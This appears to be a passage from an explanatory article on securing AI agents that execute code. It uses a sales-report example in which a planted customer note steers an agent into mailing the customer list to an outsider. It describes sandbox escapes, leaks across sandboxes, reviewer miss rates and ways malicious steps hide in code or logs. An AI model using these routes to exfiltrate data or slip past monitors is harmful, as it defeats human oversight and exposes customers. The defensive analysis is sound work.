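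The Vercel flaw was in the Linux kernel's networking code, which almost every large cloud company uses to keep customers apart. Anthropic recommends widely used components like this one. They are still preferable because many more people look for flaws in them, but they aren't impenetrable. Simpler mistakes can also expose data. Cloudflare (2026) fixed its container service after researchers found that a new container could expose data left on the disk by an earlier one.

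The model writing the code may also be good at finding such flaws. The researcher who found the kernel flaw used GPT-5.6 Sol as his main reasoning engine, directing the work and checking its findings himself. Anthropic says its own models have sometimes escaped a sandbox to complete a task, with no attacker involved. An agent's sandbox therefore has to withstand more than a fixed piece of malicious code, because the model can read an error message and try something else.

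If the sales code escaped from a server container, the damage would depend on what else was on that server. A developer can reduce the damage by running the container on a machine that never holds the customer list or the database login. An escape would then not give the attacker everything the original agent had.

### What a steered agent can still do

Even a perfect sandbox doesn't change what the model reads, so the customer's note can still steer it. The model might leave the West region out of the chart, include customers' names or tell the manager it checked figures it never looked at. These actions require only the order file and the chart, which the code needs for its job.

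The sandbox also has no control over tools that the harness runs elsewhere, so `email_chart` still needs its list of six recipients.

Using several sandboxes can allow a data leak that no single one would allow. For example, one sandbox might hold sales data but have no network access, while another can browse the web but holds no data. The model can copy customers' names from the first sandbox's output into a program it runs in the second, and that program can send the names out over the internet.

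## What people can check under each design

A sandbox can't detect errors such as a chart that leaves out the West region, so someone still has to check the agent's work. A company can have people approve each action as it happens, read a whole program before it runs, or check the boundary, which is the set of files, network addresses, logins and tools the agent can use.

### What the reviewer sees

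If the unrestricted sales agent has to ask the manager before it runs any code, the manager gets three requests for the report. The first program prints 20 rows of the sales table, which is how the customer's note reaches the model. A careful reviewer would still approve it, because printing rows is harmless in itself. The second program draws the chart. If the model has followed the note, the third contains the altered `send_mail` call from the original attack.

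To catch the theft, the manager has to read Python, notice that one address is outside the company and work out what the attached `customers.csv` contains. Anthropic gives a harder example, `find . -name "*.tmp" -exec rm {} \;`, which deletes every file ending in `.tmp` in a folder and its subfolders.

With fixed tools, the harness can show the user a question such as "Email the third-quarter chart for all regions to the finance director?", which anyone who knows what they asked for can answer.

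When the model writes the whole program first, a reviewer can read all 14 lines before any of them runs. They can see that only the finance director and the operations manager could receive the email, and under what condition. They need to know Python and how the company's functions work, such as whether `get_sales` leaves out returned orders. They can't tell from the program that half the western orders have "W" in the region column.

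If the agent runs its code on a separate machine, an administrator might check a list like this:

```
read:     orders-2026-Q3.csv
write:    chart.png
network:  none
logins:   none
mail:     email_chart, six permitted recipients
```

This doesn't require knowing Python, but it does require some knowledge of security, such as that a site approved for downloading packages may also accept uploads. The administrator can't tell from the list whether the chart is right.

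The designs also differ in how much there is to read. If the manager wants the report every week for a year, and every program works the first time, the totals are:

| Design | What there is to check in a year | Who could judge it |
|---|---|---|
| Unrestricted agent | 156 programs | A programmer who knows the company's data |
| Fixed tools | 104 tool calls, or the list of 720 possible emails once | The sales manager |
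| Separate coding agent | 104 programs, and the orchestrator's instructions for them | A programmer who knows the company's data |
| Program written first | 52 programs | A programmer who knows the company's data |
| Code generated and reviewed in advance | One program, and every repair to it | A programmer who knows the company's data |
| Separate machine | One boundary, and every change to it | A security administrator |

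### How carefully people approve actions

Anthropic's usage data showed that Claude Code users approved about 93% of permission prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a newer figure of 97%. Anthropic attributes this partly to approval fatigue, in which people pay less attention to each prompt as they see more of them.

To count a reviewer's mistakes, researchers have to know which requests were dangerous. They can't treat every approval as an error, because if 97 of every 100 requests are safe, a perfect reviewer will approve 97.

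Anthropic tested whether people refuse dangerous commands in permission prompts. In the study, 1,053 paid testers worked on coding tasks in an environment set up for the purpose. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, and 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

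The testers had less reason to be careful than programmers working on their own files, but they did know they were being evaluated, though not for what. Anthropic was also arguing for replacing these prompts with an automatic reviewer. Even so, the result is so poor that a company shouldn't rely on frequent prompts to stop an attack.

A sandbox reduces the number of permission prompts because commands that stay within its boundary can run without approval. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* reports 84% fewer prompts in the company's internal use of Claude Code. That figure doesn't measure whether people judge the remaining prompts any better.

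People also change how they supervise as they gain experience. In Anthropic's anonymised data, experienced users approved actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but they also interrupted the agent more often. This approach makes sense for work they can undo, such as editing a file under version control. It wouldn't protect the customer list, because the manager can't stop an email that has already been sent. Anthropic adds that users find it harder to notice an agent going off course as its commands become more ambitious, and that this kind of supervision will probably work less well with several agents.

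Many users avoid the prompts. Anthropic found that by June 2026, about half of active command-line users had created a rule that automatically allows certain shell commands. Many of these rules allow any Python program, which is almost the same as allowing everything. A sales manager who created such a rule while approving the harmless program that prints 20 rows would also have approved the program that mails the customer list. A quarter of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips permission prompts.

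NVIDIA advises developers to require new approval each time an agent tries to do something that breaks its isolation, such as opening a network connection. This closes the gap left by standing rules, but it can bring back approval fatigue if the agent needs a connection every few minutes.

### What an automatic reviewer misses

Claude Code's auto mode has another model review most risky actions in place of the user. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that this model first makes a quick decision that errs towards blocking, then reasons more carefully about anything it flagged. It receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or tool results. For the sales report, it would receive a request for a chart and a program that mails `customers.csv` to an outsider, but not the customer's note, so the note couldn't persuade it.

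The reviewer caught about 83% of overeager actions, in which an agent trying to help does something dangerous that the user hadn't authorised, such as using a login it happened to find. It missed the other 17%, but the test used only 52 real examples, so the true miss rate could plausibly be about 9% to 30%. If an agent attempted four such actions during a task, and the reviewer's chance of catching each one didn't depend on the others, at least one would get through about half the time (1 − 0.83⁴ ≈ 0.53).

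The 83% doesn't measure how often agents attempt these actions, and it doesn't mean that 17% of everything the agent does is dangerous. The reviewer blocked 0.4%, or about 40, of 10,000 ordinary tool calls by Anthropic's staff.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. If the sales manager wrote "make sure everyone who needs the figures gets them", the reviewer might take that as permission to mail the figures to an outside address.

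When Anthropic gave the automatic reviewer the same dangerous commands it had given the paid testers, the reviewer blocked 937 of the 1,053, or 89%. The testers had refused only six of the 116 commands that the reviewer allowed, so using both would have stopped 943. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested the reviewer by inserting deliberate attacks into records of real coding sessions. The reviewer missed 12% of the attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it. Among attacks Anthropic had never seen, the improved version caught about half of those the original had missed.

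Evidence from everyday use is weaker. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had already flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained a seriously harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different kinds of work.

The test with paid testers used single commands, while a long program gives an attacker more places to hide a harmful step. The reviewer in auto mode is instructed to judge what a script does, not just the command that runs it. But automated review of whole programs is still far from reliable. In *Compiled AI*, for example, the security scanners missed a quarter of the deliberately vulnerable programs.

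### Whether a program is easier to audit

When the manager approves one action at a time, they don't know what the agent will do next. They might let it read the customer list without knowing that it will later mail the list to an outsider.

A reviewer with the complete program can look for every operation that sends something and trace where its recipients and attachments come from. The sales program has only one such operation, `send_mail`. The company can also keep the approved version, run exactly that version, and compare any later version with it line by line.

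People seem to scrutinise plans more than individual actions. Anthropic reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents, but only 3% of permission prompts. But a plan may contain no code, and a user may reject it because they want a different feature, not because they noticed a danger.

The main drawback of a program for a reviewer is that one approval can cover many operations. The sales program sends a quarantined model a query about each order, so approving its 14 lines could approve thousands of queries. If the harness shows the reviewer only a command such as `python report.py`, they approve everything in the file without seeing any of it.

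A generated program may also be too long to check thoroughly. The programs that Foerster and colleagues used to operate a computer averaged 213 lines and 40 branches. If each branch could go either way independently, a program with 40 branches could run in about a trillion (2⁴⁰) ways. For the sales program, a reviewer can save time by checking only the operations that send, delete or pay for something, but this doesn't work for a program made of clicks.

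Malicious code can also look ordinary. The model could save the customer list as `regions.csv` and attach it to the report, or send the report to an outside address that differs from the finance director's by one letter. OWASP, an organisation that publishes advice on software security, also warns in its *Secure Coding with AI Cheat Sheet* about invisible characters that can mislead a person reading the code.

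Reviewers also tend to look only at the change they asked for. Suppose the manager asks for different chart colours, and the agent also adds an address to the file of permitted recipients. A reviewer checking the colours could easily miss it. OWASP calls this the most common failure in reviewing coding agents' work, though it gives no figures. It recommends automatic checks that flag changes outside the requested scope. These checks matter even with auto mode, which lets the agent edit files in the project folder without consulting the automatic reviewer, on the assumption that a person can look at the changes later.

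Passing tests provide little reassurance if the agent that wrote the code also wrote the tests. OWASP notes that agents sometimes delete a failing test or rewrite it to accept the wrong answer. For the sales report, comparing the results with the finance department's confirmed totals is a better check.

### Finding out what happened

Suppose the team with an orchestrator, a coder and a terminal has sent out the customer list, and the company wants to know why. The orchestrator's log contains its instructions and the coder's report of success. The terminal's log contains the program. The database recorded a query from the company's account, and the mail server recorded an authorised message. The cause is in the 20 rows that the terminal posted. If the logs don't share a task number, an investigator has to match the entries by time.

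The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written with cyber agencies from the United States, Canada, New Zealand and Britain, describes a similar problem with agents that jointly approve payments. Each agent makes part of the decision and the logs are fragmented, so it is hard to tell which agent caused a mistake. Agents may also create sub-agents that the operators don't know about.

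The agencies recommend a single audit log of all messages between agents, and a separate identity for each agent. With separate identities, the database log would show whether the coder or the orchestrator had requested the customer list. Agents should not have permission to write to the logs, and a person should review any request to delete them. Even a complete log may be hard to use because, as the agencies point out, agents produce large amounts of repetitive text, which can hide the few entries that matter.

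Important information may also never reach the orchestrator. In Triedman and colleagues' tests, some coding agents recognised malicious code but reported success without mentioning the danger. Anthropic's auto mode checks both ends of a handoff. When the main agent delegates a task, the reviewer checks whether the user wanted it. The reviewer has to do this before the handoff because the main agent's instruction appears in the sub-agent's record as the user's own, which makes any task look authorised.

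When the sub-agent finishes, the reviewer reads the full record of its actions and adds a warning to its result if something looks wrong. By then the sub-agent may already have sent an email, and the main agent can still ignore the warning. A stricter harness could pause the task until a person has read the warning.

Isolation can make an agent harder for a company's security team to monitor. Many companies use endpoint detection and response software, which monitors the processes on a computer for signs of an attack. Anthropic says that Cowork's virtual machine appears to this software as a single process, and that the software can't inspect anything inside it. Administrators can retrieve event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this isn't live monitoring, so a company might not discover a theft until the next day. The usual security software can monitor a stored program as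 it runs on an ordinary company server.

Companies also need to decide who is responsible for the code. OWASP wants every AI-generated change to have a human owner who has reviewed and understood it, with a record of who approved it and which tool and model produced it. A programmer can take that responsibility for a stored sales program they have read, but a sales manager who can't read Python can't take it for a new program every week.

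### What official guidance asks for

In December 2025, OWASP (2025) published a list of the ten most critical security risks for AI agents, developed with more than 100 experts. One of them is unexpected code execution. Velida, in *Preventing Unexpected Code Execution in AI Agents*, quotes the recommendations for it, which include:

- banning `eval` in production agents and using safe interpreters
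- running code in a sandbox with limited network access, and never with administrator rights
- separating the generation of code from its execution, with checks between them
- requiring human approval for runs with elevated privileges
- keeping a version-controlled list of what may run automatically.

The unrestricted sales agent follows almost none of this advice. Adding a coder and a terminal separates writing code from running it, but this meets the recommendation only if something checks the program before it runs. In Magentic-One, that check is optional. There is a natural time to check a stored program, or one written before any customer's text arrives.

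Another risk on the list is that attackers will mislead the person giving approval. Palo Alto Networks' *OWASP Agentic AI Top 10 Survival Guide* describes how they can use false explanations of what an agent is doing to exploit people's trust in it. The harness should therefore take the recipient and attachments from the tool call and show those in the permission prompt, not the agent's description of them.

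The guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners covers agents generally and has no separate section on code execution. It recommends sandboxes, minimal permissions and explicit control flows that keep an agent within its authorised task. It also suggests separate roles for agents that coordinate, read and act. It advises organisations to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and never to give them broad access to sensitive data. A sales agent set up this way would have no login that could read the customer list.

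The agencies want human approval for actions that are hard to reverse or have serious consequences, such as deleting important records or sending data out of the network. They add that designers or operators, not the agent, should decide which actions need approval. The paid testers rarely caught dangerous commands, so approval requests are more likely to help if they are infrequent and easy to understand. For the sales report, the harness could mail charts to the five recipients inside the company without asking. Before sending one to the outside auditor, it could show the manager the chart and the auditor's name and wait for an answer.
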